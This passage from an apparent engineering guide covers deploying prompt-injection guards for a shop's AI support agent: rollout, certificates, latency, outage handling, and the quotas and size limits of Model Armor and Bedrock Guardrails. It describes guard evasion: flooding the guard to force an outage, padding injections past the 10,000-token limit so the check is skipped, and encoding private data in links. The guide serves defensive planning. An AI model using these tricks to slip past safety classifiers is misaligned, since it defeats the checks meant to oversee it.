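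PayPal's gateways check for new rules in this way and keep the last working version if an update fails to load. Administrators can see the version they saved and the version the gateways are enforcing. Meshlib goes further by requiring the library to confirm each numbered set of rules before taking over from the proxy. Until then, Cilium's proxy keeps enforcing the rules, so a library that starts late doesn't leave a gap in enforcement.

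### Detector versions, certificates and distance

A new detector is much larger than a list of rules. AgentRedGuard's 142 million parameters take up about 284 MB at two bytes each, so sending it to 200 nodes transfers about 57 GB. The threshold has to ship in the same package as the model, since retraining can change which threshold works best.

PayPal first runs new spending rules in "shadow mode", where the gateway records which requests it would have blocked but lets them through. The shop could test a detector the same way on a few nodes. Long connections slow the final switch to new software. Voice calls through PayPal's gateway can last 30 minutes, so an old copy gets up to an hour to finish its calls before it shuts down. PayPal made more than ten updates during live calls without dropping a call, but old and new software may run side by side for up to an hour.

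Sidecars also need certificates. Suppose each certificate lasts 24 hours and the sidecar renews it after 12. With 2,000 sidecars, the mesh issues 4,000 certificates a day. If the issuing service fails, certificates start to expire after 12 hours, and components then refuse each other's connections. New components can't join the mesh during the outage because they have no certificate. The signing key for decrypting outgoing traffic needs more protection, so the shop should keep it on a few egress proxies rather than on the 200 nodes.

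Distance adds a delay that faster hardware can't remove. Light travels about 200 km per millisecond in optical fibre, so a round trip to a guard 6,000 km away takes at least 60 ms. Ten checks in series would add at least 600 ms of travel time, compared with 50 ms if each round trip took 5 ms. The shop could send several texts together to save trips, but Kong's *AI GCP Model Armor* warns that combining messages reduces accuracy with Google's guard. Sending separate checks in parallel is safer, as is putting a guard in each region, though regional guards mean more copies to update.

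### When the guard is unavailable

Suppose the shop's guard stops for 10 minutes, during which about 6,944 requests arrive at the average rate. If the guard fails closed, none of those customers gets an answer. If it fails open, they all get unchecked answers. With 100 bad links among 1,000,000 daily answers, fewer than one of those unchecked answers would contain a bad link on average.

That calculation favours failing open, but it assumes the outage is accidental. An attacker may be able to cause an outage by flooding the guard with long texts, then send the injection while the guard is down.

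The damage also depends on the action, so the shop doesn't need one rule for everything. During an outage, it could respond as follows:

| Step | Response while the guard is down |
|---|---|
| Answer without a link | Show it |
| Answer with a link | Show the text and remove the link |
| Order lookup with a fixed schema | Allow it |
| Opening an outside page | Refuse |
| Refund | Hold it for a member of staff |

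Sasidharan and colleagues divide failures in a similar way. Their gateway refuses requests if it can't check access or search for private data, but keeps serving customers if the program that collects measurements fails. The shop could also switch to a simpler backup, such as the written rules inside the gateway.

If a guard fails closed, requests that depend on it fail whenever it is down. A guard that works 99.9% of the time is down for about 43 minutes in a 30-day month. If a refund has to pass three such guards and their outages don't overlap, refunds stop for about 130 minutes that month.

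The defaults for handling failed checks vary even for the same detector. According to Google Cloud's *Integrate Model Armor with Gemini Enterprise Agent Platform*, the platform skips the check and continues if Model Armor is unreachable, has an internal error or isn't available in the region. Quota and permission problems still produce errors. LiteLLM, an open-source gateway that can call the same Google service, by default blocks requests when the call fails and attachments that it can't send for scanning.

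A guard that fails open may show no sign of it. Promptfoo's *Testing Google Cloud Model Armor* notes that a successful answer from Google's platform doesn't prove the screening ran. It advises operators to turn on logging and count skipped checks separately from clean results. The shop should also disconnect its guard before launch and see what happens to a test refund.

### Limits of managed guards

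Providers limit how often customers can call a guard and how much text it will read. These are the documented defaults for Model Armor and two interfaces to Amazon Bedrock Guardrails:

| Service | Date | Calls | Text |
|---|---|---|---|
| Model Armor | August 2026 | 1,200 a minute per project, or 600 through integrations with other Google services | 4 MB, with 10,000 tokens for injection detection and 130,000 for private data |
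| Amazon's ApplyGuardrail | February 2025 | 50 a second in two US regions | 200 "text units" a second for most filters |
| Amazon's InvokeGuardrailChecks | 2026 | 1,500 a minute per account and region | Limits on length not included here |

The first row comes from Google Cloud, the second from AWS's *Amazon Bedrock Guardrails announces an increase in service quota limits* (2025) and the third from AWS's *Quotas*. *Quotas* also warns that AWS may reject a sudden burst of calls even if the total for the minute is below the limit.

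The shop receives an average of 694 requests a minute. Checking only the question and the answer takes 1,389 calls a minute, which is already above Model Armor's default quota. Checking all ten texts from the refund example takes 6,944. Google says customers can usually request a higher quota, but the shop should do so before its busiest season. It should also plan for the evening rush, when traffic is above the average.

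The size limits create a way around the guard. If Model Armor's injection filter finds nothing in a text of more than 10,000 tokens, it returns EXECUTION_SKIPPED instead of NO_MATCH_FOUND. An attacker could put a long harmless passage before the injection, and the text would get through if the shop's software blocks only on MATCH_FOUND. The software should treat a skipped check as a failure, or split long texts before sending them to Model Armor.

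Model Armor scans only the first 256 URLs in a prompt or answer. A support answer never needs that many, so the shop can reject any that has more. Model Armor also doesn't decode Base64 or URL encoding, and it judges each prompt or answer without the rest of the conversation, so it could miss private data that the model encoded in a link or spread over several answers. For Amazon's newer interface, AWS's *Amazon Bedrock Guardrails announces a new API targeting agentic AI workflows* (2026) lists checks for harmful content, prompt attacks and private data, but not for malicious links, so the shop would need a separate reputation lookup for those.

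A guard service's limits can change within months. Google Cloud's *Model Armor release notes* list a limit of 2,000 tokens for all filters in May 2025 and 10,000 for injection detection that July. According to an older description by the developer hi120ki, the service processed up to 40 URLs per request. Operators should test the current limits with texts just below and just above them.

Google charges for Model Armor by the token and doesn't charge for data the guard skips. Checking long retrieved passages can therefore cost more than checking the answer, and an unexpectedly low bill may mean that the guard is skipping text.

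### Sending private text to an outside guard

A guard has to receive a message to check it for a home address, so using another company's guard sends private data outside the shop. By default, the open-source gateway Agentgateway sends Model Armor the system prompt, messages and tool results. In the refund example, that includes the delivery record. The shop can exclude tool results, but then the guard doesn't receive the courier's note and can't detect an injection in it.

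Google says Model Armor processes text in memory and discards it after the check, unless the customer turns on logging. Logs may contain pieces of the text, which conflicts with the advice to use logs to find skipped checks. The shop should therefore record verdicts and error codes and leave out the text where the settings allow it.

Where a check runs can also matter. Google Cloud doesn't offer malicious URL detection in regions with strict local processing, because the feature relies on services that may handle data elsewhere. An organization that must keep data in such a region needs another way to check links. AWS's *Amazon Bedrock Guardrails now supports cross-region inference* (2025) describes an option that moves guardrail checks between regions to absorb bursts of traffic. A tester for Classmethod's *Amazon Bedrock Guardrails がクロスリージョン推論をサポートしました* found no way to see which region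 had processed a check.

The shop can send out less private data by finding and replacing it first. PayPal searches for private data with its own rules and model before a request leaves its network, and it can replace private values reversibly, much as FINOS describes. The shop could do the same before calling an outside injection detector, which can recognise a suspicious instruction without the customer's real address. The substitution will miss some values, as Sasidharan and colleagues say of their own detector.
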